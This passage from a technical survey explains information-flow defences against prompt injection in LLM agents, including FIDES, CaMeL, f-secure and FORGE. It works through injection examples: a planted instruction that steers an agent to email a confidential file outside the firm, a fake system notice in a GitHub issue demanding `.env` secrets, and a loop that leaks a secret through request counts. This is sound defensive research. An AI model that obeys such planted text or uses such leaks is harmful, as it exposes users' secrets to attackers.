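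Line 5, which handles the model, is the most cautious step. Like FORGE, FIDES treats everything the model received as a possible influence on its reply, so the reply gets every label in the history. If the agent has read ten documents and quotes only the first, the quotation still carries the labels of all ten. Rotenberg's Privacy Restriction Processor, a 1974 design described by Denning, did the same for ordinary programs by giving each process the join of the labels of everything it had read. For agents, Siddiqui and others have proposed a less cautious method that finds the few messages that mattered to a reply, generates the reply again from those alone, and labels it accordingly. Costa and colleagues say their framework could accommodate this, but they leave it out for simplicity.

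Line 7 checks the call before the tool runs. If the call fails the check, the basic algorithm aborts the run. In the experiments, the agent instead received a notice of the refusal and could continue.

Lines 9 and 10 label the tool's output and any data it stores for later. Suppose a planted instruction makes the agent copy a confidential file into a new file, `notes.txt`, and then read the notes back to try to get a copy without the confidential label. Line 10 labels the notes confidential when the agent writes them, and line 9 carries that label over when the agent reads them. This works only if the list of what each tool may read and write is complete.

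A designer can also do some of the checking before the program runs. Denning favoured having a compiler certify a program's flows in advance, partly because a program checked at run time can leak data by deliberately causing violations, if the program's owner can see the record of refused operations. In a similar approach for agents by Zhou and colleagues, the model writes its next steps as a short Haskell program, and a type-checker rejects the program before it runs if it could have effects that its declared type doesn't permit. They use LIO, an existing Haskell library, to control information flow. Developers must also write the surrounding application in Haskell, which will put off many of them.

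### Two policies on labelled calls

The loop does not specify the policy at line 7. Costa and colleagues give two basic policies, both for labels of the form (integrity, readers), where integrity is T for trusted or U for untrusted.

The trusted-action policy applies to consequential calls, such as payments or emails. Let ℓ_f be the label on the choice of tool and ℓ₁ to ℓₙ the labels on the arguments. The monitor permits the call only if

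ℓ_f ⊔ ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ = (T, any readers)

Because one U makes the whole join U, this rule requires that nothing untrusted influenced the decision to call the tool or any of its arguments.

The permitted-reader policy applies to calls that send data somewhere. Let *R* be the set of people who will be able to read what goes through the channel, for instance the recipients of an email or the members of a group chat. The monitor permits the call only if the label on the data has the form

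(any integrity, *S*) with *S* ⊑ *R*, that is, *R* ⊆ *S*

Everybody at the other end must already have the right to read the data.

The permitted-reader policy limits what a successful prompt injection can achieve, but it does not prevent the injection. An attacker can still take over the agent and have it delete appointments or send a colleague forty emails, but can't have it send the budget to someone who isn't permitted to read it. The same limit would apply if the model made a mistake without an attacker.

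The trusted-action policy does stop injected text from causing consequential calls, including harmful ones that reveal nothing, such as a payment to a stranger. But on its own, it lets the agent send a secret to an outsider if the agent has read nothing untrusted. Costa and colleagues relate this to robust declassification, an idea from research on programming languages. Declassification means deliberately relaxing a confidentiality label, and it is robust if an attacker can't cause it. They argue that one can assume a release of secret data is intentional when the context contains no untrusted data. That assumption is fair with regard to attackers but weaker with regard to language models, which, they note, misread users and make unnecessary calls even when all the data is trusted.

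With both policies in force, an email goes out only if no untrusted text influenced it and every recipient is allowed to read its contents.

### The vendor's document with labels

In the running example, the user is Ana, and only she and her colleague Ben may read the confidential file. The vendor's document is public. The table shows the label on each new message and the context label after that message, with "all" for data that anyone may read.

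| Event | Label of the message | Context label afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| Ana's request | (T, all) | (T, all) |
| Call to read the vendor's document | (T, all) | (T, all) |
| The document, with the planted instruction | (U, all) | (U, all) |
| Call to read the confidential file | (U, all) | (U, all) |
| The confidential file | (U, {Ana, Ben}) | (U, {Ana, Ben}) |
| Call to email the file to the outside address | (U, {Ana, Ben}) | (U, {Ana, Ben}) |

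The confidential file is itself trustworthy, but it enters the conversation as untrusted because line 9 joins the label of the call to the label of the file. This makes some sense, since the vendor's text may have determined which file the agent opened, and an attacker could benefit from steering the agent to an outdated one. The monitor allows the call that reads the file unless someone has classed reading as a consequential action.

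It refuses the email under either policy. The call is untrusted, and the outside address belongs to neither Ana nor Ben.

The policies come apart on other emails that the same agent might send:

| Email | Label of the call | Trusted-action policy | Permitted-reader policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Summary of the vendor's document, to Ana | (U, all) | refuses | allows |
| Confidential file, to the attacker | (U, {Ana, Ben}) | refuses | refuses |
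| Confidential file, to the firm's auditor, as Ana asked; no outside text read | (T, {Ana, Ben}) | allows | refuses |
| Confidential file, to Ben, as Ana asked; no outside text read | (T, {Ana, Ben}) | allows | allows |

The first row is the email that Ana wanted. The trusted-action policy blocks it even if the vendor planted nothing, because the agent wrote the summary after reading the vendor's text. Costa and colleagues encounter the same problem with a request to summarise three emails and post the summary to Slack. Their full system avoids this by keeping untrusted text in variables that the planner never reads.

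A less restrictive option is to require only one of the two conditions. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, a post by a team that includes several of the researchers behind FIDES, gives a sample policy for a tool that sends messages to a Teams channel. The policy allows a message if the context is trusted or if all current members of the channel may read the contents. Otherwise it asks the user. It would allow all of the four emails except the one to the attacker. Unless the context is trusted, the policy still asks the user before releasing data to new readers, so an injection can't cause such a release by itself. However, a stranger's text may shape a message to permitted readers, so the summary that Ana receives could contain whatever the vendor wanted her to believe.

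The permitted-reader policy also covers the budget example. Once the agent has opened the budget, its emails carry the label {Ana, Ben}. The vendor isn't in that set, so the monitor refuses any email to the vendor, even an honest one that only asks about the price. In this run, the flow rule does no better than a ban on outside email. Over many runs it does better, because it restricts the agent only after the budget has entered the conversation, and only towards people who may not read it, while a ban would always block email to everyone outside.

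Labels also help a person decide whether to approve an exception. Microsoft suggests that a monitor with labels can show Ana where untrusted data came from, what the email would disclose and who would see that information for the first time. The message in the sample policy provides part of this by listing the people who would gain access.

Some leaks need no attacker. In another of Microsoft's examples, Alex asks an agent to deal with his unanswered emails. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't supposed to know the figures yet, has written to ask about them. An obliging agent might simply tell him. After the agent has read both emails, its replies carry the label

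{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}

and the monitor won't let it answer Marco without asking Alex. Had Priya copied Marco in on her email, the label would be {Alex, Marco} and the reply could go. An allow-list could hardly state this. Marco is a proper recipient for most of what Alex writes, and whether he may have this reply depends on who received a different email.

### FIDES in Microsoft's Agent Framework

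Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced on 20 May that FIDES had become part of Agent Framework, the company's toolkit for building agents, as an experimental feature that developers have to switch on. The labels are somewhat simpler than in the paper. Data is trusted or untrusted, and its confidentiality is public, private or, for the most sensitive personal data, `user_identity`. Because the scheme uses levels instead of lists of readers, it can keep private data out of public places but could not distinguish between Priya and Marco.

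The announcement gives the example of an agent that sorts bug reports (issues) on GitHub. The agent can read issues, read and write files in the repository, and post public comments. An attacker files an issue that looks like an ordinary complaint about a failed build on a Mac. The issue ends with a paragraph made to look like a system notice, which claims that a maintainer has authorised access to secrets for debugging. It tells the agent to open `.env`, where developers commonly keep passwords and keys, and to post the contents as a reply.

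The agent reads the issue, and the context becomes untrusted and public. If the model follows the notice and requests the file, the monitor allows the request, and the context becomes untrusted and private. The agent then tries to post the comment. The developer has declared that the comment tool accepts only public data, so the monitor blocks the call before it runs. If the notice had instead contained an instruction to overwrite a file, the monitor would have blocked that call too, because the tool for writing files doesn't accept calls influenced by untrusted data. A blocked call fails or goes to a human for approval, depending on a setting.

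The sample code applies the paper's two policies to different tools, limiting confidentiality for the comment tool and requiring trust for the file tool. The opening of the announcement describes a stricter rule that blocks all comments while untrusted content is in the agent's context. Under that rule, an agent that sorts strangers' bug reports could never reply to one. The code doesn't enforce it, so an attacker who doesn't try to extract secrets can still influence what the agent says in public.

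Microsoft lists several weaknesses that it hopes to fix. The framework treats output from unlabelled tools as trusted and public. Once an untrusted issue enters the context, the rest of the run counts as untrusted unless the developer explicitly drops the issue. The approval prompts are also coarse. Microsoft advises developers not to use FIDES if all their data comes from one trusted source and goes to one trusted destination, or if the agent has no privileged tools and can at worst give a wrong answer.

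In its later post, Microsoft extends the work to other products but still calls the software it describes, including the Agent Framework module, prototypes. GitHub's server for connecting agents to its site can now label what it returns, if the developer asks for labels. It marks files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal, has an experimental setting that keeps a context label and checks calls against it. With this setting on, an agent that has read both a public issue and a private repository can't post in public on its own, but one that stays within public repositories, or within private ones, can work without interruption. The setting covers only some of the tools on GitHub's server and none on other servers.

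## Designs that separate planning from untrusted data

In the simplest version of FIDES, a single document from a stranger makes the context untrusted for the rest of the run. The trusted-action policy then blocks every later payment, email or other consequential call, including the summary that Ana asked for. Kim, Choi and Lee (2025) point out in *Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* that measuring how much one text influenced a later call usually requires inspecting the model's internals, which most commercial services don't allow. A monitor therefore can't easily tell which of those calls the document affected.

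The designs in this section keep untrusted text away from the planner and let another component read it. They rely on a distinction between control flow (here, the choice and order of tool calls) and data flow (the values passed between calls). Kim and colleagues show how each can become unsafe without any planted command. If a user asks for an emailed summary of the news, a false article can end up in the email, which is an unsafe data flow. If the user asks the agent to find a program's installation guide and follow it, a fake guide can determine which commands the agent runs, which is an unsafe control flow.

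### Two models and a controller

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, began with rules for any model that reads untrusted text. The model should have no tools that an attacker could abuse. If it might also see private data, it should produce no links or images, because a web address can carry data to whoever runs the site. A model under these rules is safe but makes a poor assistant, so Willison proposed two models. The privileged model has the tools and takes its input from trusted sources, mainly the user. The quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools, and the designer assumes that an attacker could take control of it at any time. Ordinary software, called the controller, passes data between the two models.

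With the vendor's document, the run would go like this:

1. The privileged model requests the document. The controller fetches it, stores it as `$VAR1` and tells the privileged model only that name.
2. The privileged model requests a summary of `$VAR1` from the quarantined model. The controller fills in the text, runs the quarantined model and stores the result as `$VAR2`.
3. The privileged model requests an email to Ana with `$VAR2` as the body. The controller fills in the summary and sends it.

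The planted instruction reaches only the quarantined model, which can't open the confidential file or send anything. The privileged model never receives the instruction, so the instruction can't prompt it to request the file. The attacker can still corrupt the summary.

The design works only if the privileged model never receives the quarantined model's free text, since that text may repeat an injection. Willison allows one exception, when the quarantined model sorts a text into one of a fixed set of categories and the controller checks that the output is exactly one of them before passing it on.

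He called his own proposal "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single programming mistake that leaks untrusted text to the privileged model undoes the protection. It also doesn't protect a user who pastes a stranger's text into the request. And the quarantined model's output could still trick the user, for instance by showing private data in encoded form and promising a funny picture to anyone who pastes it into a certain website.

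### f-secure

Willison described a pattern in prose, without saying exactly what it guarantees. *System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao, 2024) gave a formal definition and a design, f-secure, meant to satisfy it. The f-secure planner also sees more than Willison's because it may read tool results labeled as trusted.

The f-secure planner writes one step at a time in a fixed format. Each step names the tool or model that will run it, the data it needs and the expected output. After the step runs, a security monitor keeps the result in temporary memory and adds a reference such as `{Data_output:1}` to the record. A later step can use that reference as input without the planner reading the data. The component that runs the steps follows fixed rules and can call only the tool or model that the step names, with only the data that the step lists.

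Before the planner writes its next step, the monitor checks each stored result and passes only the trusted ones to the planner. Wu and colleagues give the example of a user who asks the agent to read emails about company budgets and notify the manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. The search finds two emails from colleagues, whom the user trusts, and one from an attacker, which contains an instruction to send all the budgets to an outside address. The planner receives only the colleagues' emails and can decide from them whether to notify the manager. A monitor that accepted or rejected the search results as a whole would have to withhold all three emails, leaving the planner with nothing to base its decision on.

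The property that Wu and colleagues want is called execution trace non-compromise. The execution trace is the sequence of steps that the system carries out. Let Q₁ and Q₂ be two versions of all the information the system can access, identical in their trusted parts and different in their untrusted parts. The property holds if, for every user request *q* and every trace π,

Pr[π | *q*, Q₁] = Pr[π | *q*, Q₂]

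An attacker who rewrites untrusted data therefore can't change how likely any sequence of steps is, but can still change the data inside a step, such as the text of a summary.

Wu and colleagues give a proof that f-secure has this property. Costa and colleagues object that its practical implementation lets insecure implicit flows taint the plans. An implicit flow passes information through a system's actions, without copying any text.

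An attacker can probably influence f-secure's traces through its error handling. When a step fails, the monitor asks the planner for a new one, and only successful steps enter the trace. Suppose the planner would choose tool A 90% of the time and tool B otherwise, and the attacker writes a file that makes tool A crash. The planner then keeps trying until it chooses B, so B appears in every trace that gets past this point, instead of the usual 10%. The file changes the trace probabilities even though the planner never reads it, so hiding the text is not enough to satisfy the definition. The attacker still has much less power than a prompt injection would give, because the planner proposes every step itself.

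### CaMeL

CaMeL, a 2025 system from Google DeepMind, builds on Willison's two-model design. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026), which extends CaMeL, describes how the original system works. Before any tool runs, the privileged model reads the user's request and writes the plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter executes the program and makes the tool calls. The program can call the quarantined model like any other function, usually to extract structured information from text.

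Nikolaou and colleagues give this small example:

```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email = query_ai_assistant(
    f"Extract Bob's email from: {messages}",
    EmailAddress)
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

Someone who posts in the channel can't add a line to this program, but they can post a message claiming that Bob has a new address. The quarantined model may then return the attacker's address, which is a valid `EmailAddress`, and the program sends the message there while making only the calls that the privileged model planned. Willison's pattern has the same weakness, since separating the models protects the control flow but an attacker can still change the values passed to a correctly chosen tool. In a 2025 note on his original post, Willison acknowledged that the CaMeL researchers had found a potential flaw in his design and addressed it.

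To address this, CaMeL's interpreter labels each value with where it came from (its sources) and who may read it (its readers), much like the integrity and confidentiality labels in FIDES. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, which is a Python function that receives the requested call and the labels on its arguments. The policy returns a decision to allow or deny the call, with a reason. In the example above, a policy could refuse any recipient whose address came from a channel where strangers can post.

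The program also allows more precise labels than a single label for the whole context, because the interpreter tracks which values go into each call. The address in the example depends on the channel's messages, but the text "Meeting at 3pm" was in the program from the start, so it remains trusted. A checker can also examine the plan before anything runs, as Nikolaou and colleagues do with temporal logic.

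Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, list several limitations. Like Willison's pattern, CaMeL assumes that the user's own request is harmless. It needs calls to two models, which is slow when the quarantined model has to go through ten emails separately. They also warn about side channels, which reveal data through the program's behaviour. Their simplest example is a loop:

`for i in range(secret): fetch("ping")`

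If the secret number is 40, the program requests the same page 40 times, and whoever runs the site can learn the number by counting the requests. None of the requests contains the secret, so a policy that checks only the labels on their arguments would allow them all. An error that occurs only when a secret meets some condition leaks information in the same way. Tallam and Miller propose a strict mode for loops whose length depends on a secret, in which the interpreter would block any call that changes something outside the program, or ask the user first. They also suggest capping the number of repetitions or combining the requests into one.

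### Hidden variables and typed answers in FIDES

The full version of FIDES has no program written in advance. Its planner chooses one call at a time, as in the basic loop, but some results reach it only as variable names. What Costa and colleagues add to Willison's idea is a rule for deciding which results to hide. FIDES hides an item only if showing it would raise the context label. If ℓ is the item's label and ℓ_c is the current context label, then:

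- if ℓ ⊑ ℓ_c, the planner sees the item;
- otherwise, FIDES stores the item with its label and shows the planner a new variable name.

FIDES applies the test to each field of a structured result. If an email's date is trusted and its body is not, FIDES shows a planner with a trusted context the date and replaces the body with a name such as `#read_emails_0.body`. If the context is already untrusted, FIDES shows the body too, because hiding it would gain nothing. The context label does not change in either case, so the agent keeps its permissions when it fetches a document.

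When the planner uses a variable in a call, FIDES replaces the name with the stored data and its label. The parts of one call can therefore have different labels. For the email with the summary of the vendor's document, the difference looks like this:

| Part of the call | Label in the basic loop | Label in FIDES |
|---|---|---|
| Choice of the email tool | (U, all) | (T, all) |
| Recipient (Ana) | (U, all) | (T, all) |
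| Body (the summary) | (U, all) | (U, all) |

The trusted-action policy in its basic form would still refuse this email, because it requires every argument to be trusted. But FIDES can now enforce a narrower policy, which requires a trusted label only on the choice of tool and the recipient:

ℓ_tool ⊔ ℓ_recipient = (T, any readers)

Ana gets her summary, and the vendor's text cannot affect where it is sent. This policy would have been pointless in the basic loop because all three labels were always the same.

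Variables also help with the budget example, where the basic loop blocked every email to the vendor once the agent had opened the budget. In the full version, the vendor's quote and the budget can both stay in variables while the context remains trusted and public. A quarantined model can then draft questions from the quote alone. The draft has the label (U, all), so it may go to the vendor. The planted request to mention the firm's highest price does no damage, because that model has never received the budget. Questions based on both files have the label (U, {Ana, Ben}), and the monitor still refuses to send them. (In their experiments, Costa and colleagues used variables only for untrusted data and relied on policy checks to protect confidential data.)

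A planner given only part of the data may guess at the rest. In one AgentDojo task, the user asks the agent to change a password if there has been a suspicious transaction. GPT-4o had the dates and amounts, but FIDES had hidden the descriptions, which a stranger could have written. The model treated a large payment as suspicious and changed the password without checking the description. Although the reasoning was unsound, the decision broke no rule because it rested only on trusted data.

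The planner has two ways to find out what is in a variable. The `inspect` tool shows it the contents, but the planner's context then takes on the variable's label, so the agent may lose permissions. The `query_llm` tool passes the variable to a quarantined model with a question and a required type of answer, and stores the answer in a new variable. FIDES can enforce the type through constrained decoding, which lets the model generate only tokens that fit the required format. If the type is Boolean, the answer will then be true or false, whatever instructions the variable contains.

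Costa and colleagues then make the type part of the label. They order types by how much information a value can carry:

bool ⊑ enum ⊑ string

A Boolean carries at most one bit, a choice from a list of *n* options (an enumeration) carries at most log₂ *n* bits, and a string has no fixed limit. A label such as ((U, all), bool) marks a true-or-false answer drawn from untrusted, public data. A policy can let such an answer influence a payment or a calendar entry but block an untrusted string from doing so. This generalises Willison's exception for fixed categories and allows a different limit for each tool.

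One weakness is that the type shows how much a single value can carry but not how many such values the planner sees. Joining two Boolean labels gives another Boolean label, although ten Booleans together can distinguish 1,024 cases. This is probably harmless when the planner asks its own fixed questions, and a cautious designer could also limit the number of answers. Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of the planner they tested because most AgentDojo tasks did not need it, so their experiments provide little evidence about typed answers.

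### Three classes of task

How much a planner must see depends on the task, and Costa and colleagues sort tasks on that basis. Their test is whether one fixed sequence of tool calls would work whatever the data turned out to be. Let D be the set of possible states of the user's mailbox, files and other data. For each state *d*, let S(*d*) be the set of sequences of calls, each ending in an answer to the user, that complete the task. The task is data independent if

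⋂_{d ∈ D} S(*d*) ≠ ∅

and data dependent otherwise. They divide the data-independent tasks further, according to whether some model has to read the data along the way. To compare planners, they use an informal policy under which a tool call is safe if the model generated it from trusted inputs.

**Data independent.** The user asks the agent to read the top three emails and forward them as a Slack message. With variables, two calls are enough:

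```
read_emails(number=3)
send_message(to=user, message=#read_emails_0)
```

The planner can write both lines without reading any of the emails. The basic planner makes the same two calls, but it breaks the policy because it reads the emails before making the second one.

**Data independent, with a query.** The user wants a summary of the three emails instead. The sequence of calls is still fixed, but a model has to read the emails:

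```
read_emails(number=3)
query_llm(prompt="Summarize ...", input=#read_emails_0)
send_message(to=user, message=#query_llm_0)
```

If the planner used `inspect` and wrote the summary itself, it would make the last call from an untrusted context. Using `query_llm` avoids this. Ana's request for a summary of the vendor's document belongs in this class.

In a **data-dependent** task, the right sequence of tool calls depends on the data the agent reads. For example, a user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and to create a calendar event if there is one. If the only meeting request is in a stranger's email, which asks to meet on Friday at 3pm, the right sequence includes a call that creates an event. If that email doesn't ask for a meeting, the right sequence leaves out the call. No single sequence is right in both cases, so to do the task properly, the agent has to act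 differently because of what the stranger wrote.

This conflicts with the property that Wu and colleagues defined for f-secure. Suppose the emails are untrusted, and let *p* be the probability that the agent creates an event. If untrusted data can't affect the probability of any trace, *p* is the same for both mailboxes. The agent then succeeds with probability at most *p* on the first mailbox and at most 1 − *p* on the second, so on at least one of them it succeeds no more than half the time. A better model would not change this limit, so the designer has to let some untrusted information influence the plan or give up on the task.

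FIDES lets through one bit:

```
read_emails(number=3)
query_llm(prompt="check for meeting",
          input=#read_emails_0, output=bool)
inspect(#query_llm_0)
query_llm(prompt="extract event details",
          input=#read_emails_0, output=dict)
set_event(#query_llm_1)
```

The planner inspects only the true-or-false answer. If it is true, a quarantined model extracts the date, time and guests, and the planner passes them to the calendar in a variable. The call to `set_event` still breaks the policy, because the planner has seen an untrusted Boolean. Costa and colleagues argue that a Boolean is unlikely to deliver a prompt injection, so a looser policy can permit the call. An attacker could still add a false meeting to the calendar and choose its guests, but could not make the planner do anything else. A policy on the arguments of `set_event` could also restrict the guests.

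CaMeL reaches a similar result by putting the decision in the program. In the notation of the earlier example, the plan might be:

```
emails = read_emails(3)
wanted = query_ai_assistant(
    f"Is there a meeting request in: {emails}", bool)
if wanted:
    details = query_ai_assistant(
        f"Extract the meeting details from: {emails}", Event)
    set_event(details)
```

The program is complete before any model reads the emails, so the emails can't change its text, but they do determine whether the last lines run. Untrusted data can therefore affect which actions CaMeL takes.

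When the agent has several possible responses, the quarantined model can choose from a fixed list (an enumeration) instead of returning a Boolean. Costa and colleagues suggest letting it choose between scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply and forwarding the email. Another method is to ask about each document separately. Willison describes an example from later work on design patterns, where an agent has to find this month's invoices and send them to the accounting department. A separate subagent reads each file and returns only whether it is relevant. An instruction planted in one file can affect the decision about that file but not about the others.

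Some requests don't fit any short list of options. If the user asks the agent to complete today's tasks in a to-do app, the text of the list has to determine what the agent does. The installation guide that Kim and colleagues describe is a harder case, because the user has asked the agent to run whatever commands a stranger wrote. The planner can't do these jobs without reading the text in full, which opens it to injection again. By Costa and colleagues' classification, data-dependent tasks make up 5% of AgentDojo's Workspace tasks and 10% of its Travel tasks, but about 43% of the tasks in Slack and 44% in Banking.

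### Subagents that keep some tools

A quarantined model without tools also has trouble with tasks that require following references between documents. Suppose the vendor's document refers to a price list on the vendor's website. The quarantined model can't fetch the list. The planner can, but only if it instructed the quarantined model to return links, since it can't read the document itself.

Kim and colleagues had already relaxed the complete ban on tools. Their system divides the agent into a trusted part and an untrusted part, and gives the untrusted part a restricted set of privileges. The trusted part sees an identifier in place of untrusted data, and the system checks that data further before it enters a privileged operation.

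In Language-Based Agent Control, the Haskell-based approach of Zhou and colleagues, a subagent's permissions depend on what it has read so far. LIO, the library they use, keeps a current label for each running computation, like the context label in FIDES. The function `toLabeled` runs part of a program separately, so that part's label can rise as it reads untrusted data while the main program's label stays the same. The result comes back sealed with its label, and the main program can pass it on but can't look inside without raising its own label.

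If the separate part is a call to a subagent, this resembles Willison's two models, with the sealed result in place of `$VAR2`, except that the subagent still has its tools. Each tool checks the subagent's current label before acting, so the set of calls that will succeed shrinks as the subagent reads less trustworthy or more sensitive data.

Zhou and colleagues give the example of a subagent that writes a direct message. It can read untrusted data and call tools while it works, and it returns the message sealed. The main agent, which has read nothing untrusted, chooses the recipient and hands both to a tool with this type:

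`sendDM :: User -> Labeled DCLabel Message -> DC ()`

The type shows that `sendDM` takes a user and a sealed, labelled message, and runs under LIO's information-flow rules (`DC`). The tool checks whether this message may go to this recipient. The main agent never reads the message, so an instruction hidden in it doesn't affect what the main agent does next.

They wrote low-water-mark policies for AgentDojo's Slack environment. A model that has read untrusted data can still open a web page, but it can't take a privileged action based on what the page contains. If it has read sensitive data, it can't open web pages either, because even the choice of address might reveal something. Under these policies, the subagent that reads the vendor's document could fetch the price list and include the prices in its summary. If it had opened the confidential file first, the monitor would block the request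 to the vendor's site.

Subagents can start other subagents. Haskell gives a subagent the same type as the program that started it, so the same limits apply to both. The parent can choose a stricter type for the subagent but not a looser one. In another example from Zhou and colleagues, an agent compiles a bibliography in which every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that adds an entry accepts only values of the type `Trusted Bib`, and only the function that fetches entries from DBLP can create such a value. The agent might start a subagent to look at a search result and decide how to continue. Even if the subagent misjudges the result, it can't add an invented entry, because a program that tried to would fail the type check and never run. In a test with the model Sonnet 5, none of the 925 citations produced this way had a wrong author, year or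 identifier. An ordinary agent with web search got 19 of 1,002 wrong.

CaMeL's privileged model must write its program before it sees any of the data. An agent under Language-Based Agent Control can read something, write a short program in response, and then continue, which suits tasks whose later steps can't be foreseen. The extra model calls made it about three times as slow as CaMeL on AgentDojo. The approach also depends more on correct labels. If a developer mislabels a tool in Willison's design, the quarantined model still can't call it, but a subagent compromised by an injection can call any tool that its label permits.

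## The case for invariants over states and histories

Labels record where data came from and who may read it, but some harms depend on neither. Suppose a shop's customer-service agent may issue refunds of up to $100 each, and one day it issues fifty refunds of $100, totaling $5,000. The allow-list permits every call. The amounts and account numbers come from the shop's own records, so their labels are trusted, and nobody learns anything confidential. Each refund may be reasonable by itself, but the shop never meant an agent to pay out $5,000 in a day without supervision.

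The shop can prevent this with an invariant. Let *R* be the total refunded today. The invariant is

*R* ≤ $500

and before each refund of *x* dollars, the monitor checks that *R* + *x* ≤ $500. The first five refunds bring the total to exactly $500. The sixth would bring it to $600, so the monitor blocks it, along with every $100 refund after it.

The guarantee follows by induction. The total starts each day at zero, which satisfies the condition, and the monitor allows only refunds that keep the condition true. The condition therefore holds however many refunds the agent requests and whatever text has misled the model. The cap on single refunds does not limit the total, because *n* calls can pay out 100*n* dollars. The drawback of limiting the total is that a sixth customer with a good claim has to wait for a person to approve the refund.

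The monitor also needs a reliable value for *R*. *Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo, 2026) describes a monitor that keeps counters during a session, such as the number of calls to each tool, so that a rule can compare a running total with a limit. A counter that restarts with each session would not protect the shop, since fifty sessions could issue one refund each, so *R* has to come from the shop's payment records. Two agents could also read *R* = $400 at the same moment and each pay out $100, so the check and the payment have to happen as a single step.

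### Conditions on state and conditions on order

Some invariants concern the current state of the world, such as the total of today's refunds, whether a backup exists, or whether a manager's approval is still in force. A monitor checks these by looking up the facts. Other invariants concern the order of events. For example, the agent must authenticate a customer before reading her account, or scan code before publishing it. To check these, the monitor needs the trace, the record of the run so far.

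Two rules with the same purpose can give different results if one checks the run's history and the other checks the current state. Suppose a company wants no agent to delete a database table without a backup. If the rule is that the agent must have made a backup earlier in the run, the monitor allows the deletion even when somebody has since erased that backup. It also blocks the deletion when the agent hasn't made a backup but last night's automatic one is good. A rule that a backup from the past 24 hours must currently exist gets both cases right, but only if the monitor can query the backup system and trust the answer.

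Many rules need both kinds of condition. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) gives an example for a retail agent. Before the agent opens an order, it must have successfully looked up the customer by email address, the order must exist, and the customer must own it. The last condition is about state, and without it a customer could identify herself correctly and then read anybody's orders. In one of the paper's test cases, a customer asked to return a digital camera. The agent was supervised by DynaGuard, a language model that judges whether actions comply with a written policy, but it still opened the order and disclosed its details without any authentication.

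Their other main example is a shop that refunds only to the original payment method or an existing gift card. A customer who paid by credit card insists on a refund to PayPal. Claude Sonnet 4.5 tried to make that refund, although the policy was in its system message. The trace may not show how the customer originally paid, so the monitor looks it up through a function that the shop's developers supply:

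`state(payment_method_same(order_id, payment)) == true || contains(payment, "gift_card")`

The part after `||` ("or") is looser than the English policy. It accepts any payment method whose identifier contains `gift_card`, whether or not the card exists or belongs to the customer. The refund tool may check the card's existence and ownership itself.

Rules over an agent's history appeared soon after tool-using agents did. In 2024, Balunovic and colleagues proposed that a program should check an agent's state against written security rules before every action. Invariant Guardrails, from one of the groups behind AgentDojo, matches patterns in the agent's trace, such as one call followed by another. Xiao and colleagues object that Invariant Guardrails has no formal semantics and doesn't check for conflicting rules. Most systems from 2025 and 2026 try to define such rules more precisely.

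### The event graph in FORGE

FORGE, the monitor that blocked the email of merger plans, stores the history as a graph. Each message, tool call and tool result is a node, and an edge joins two events if one may have influenced the other. Palumbo and colleagues write `DependsOn(e, d)` when event *e* may depend on event *d*. FORGE adds the edges automatically as the agent runs. A model's output depends on every message in the history it received, a tool result depends on the call that produced it, and a message between agents connects its sender's events to its receiver's.

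When several agents work at once, a graph is more informative than a chronological log. Suppose one agent reads a stranger's document at 10:00, and a second agent, which has had no contact with the first, emails an auditor at 10:01. Judging by the log alone, the document might have influenced the email because it was read first. In the graph, no path connects them, so the document doesn't taint the email. If the first agent had sent the second a note in between, there would be a path.

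The `Deny` rule given earlier for the vendor's document comes last here and relies on four others:

```
Tainted(e)   :- UntrustedInput(e).
Tainted(e)   :- DependsOn(e, d), Tainted(d).
HasSecret(e) :- SensitiveInput(e).
HasSecret(e) :- DependsOn(e, d), HasSecret(d).
Deny(a)      :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
```

The sign `:-` means "if" and a comma means "and". An event is tainted if it is itself untrusted input, or if it depends on a tainted event. The second rule is recursive, since it defines taint in terms of taint, and so it follows a chain of influence of any length. The two rules for secrets work the same way. For the run in which the agent obeys the planted instruction, they give these results (leaving out the system message):

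| Event | Depends directly on | Tainted | Has secret |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Ana's request | – | no | no |
| 2. Call to read the vendor's document | 1 | no | no |
| 3. The document | 2 | yes, as untrusted input | no |
| 4. Call to read the confidential file | 1–3 | yes, through 3 | no |
| 5. The confidential file | 4 | yes, through 4 | yes, as sensitive input |
| 6. Call to email the outside address | 1–5 | yes | yes |

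Event 6 is an external send and has both marks, so FORGE derives `Deny` and blocks the email.

The rules are written in Datalog because the agent has to wait for the result of each check. Datalog can't express every computation, but applying its rules to a finite set of facts always finishes and gives the same answer. The time this takes grows only polynomially with the number of facts, and the median check took under a millisecond on a customer-service benchmark.

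A FORGE policy can contain both `Allow` and `Deny` rules. If FORGE derives both for the same call, it blocks the call, and if it derives neither, it follows the developer's chosen default. An ordinary allow-list is therefore a FORGE policy that refuses calls by default and whose `Allow` rules mention only the call's name and arguments.

The graph records possible influence, so a missing edge is much worse than an extra one. An extra edge may cause FORGE to block a harmless call, but if an edge is missing, the rules can't connect the email with the document behind it, and an attack can go undetected.

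### Information-flow rules as a special case

`Tainted` and `HasSecret` are labels under another name. If the only integrity labels are trusted and untrusted, `Tainted(e)` holds exactly when the join of the labels on *e* and everything behind it is untrusted. The trusted-action policy from FIDES, which refuses consequential calls that untrusted data has influenced, then takes one line:

`Deny(a) :- Consequential(a), Tainted(a).`

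The permitted-reader policy needs slightly more, because its labels are lists of people. Let `Reaches(a, e)` mean that *a* depends on *e* through one or more steps, which two recursive rules can define. The policy could then read:

```
Deny(a) :- Recipient(a, p), Reaches(a, e),
           Restricted(e), not MayRead(p, e).
```

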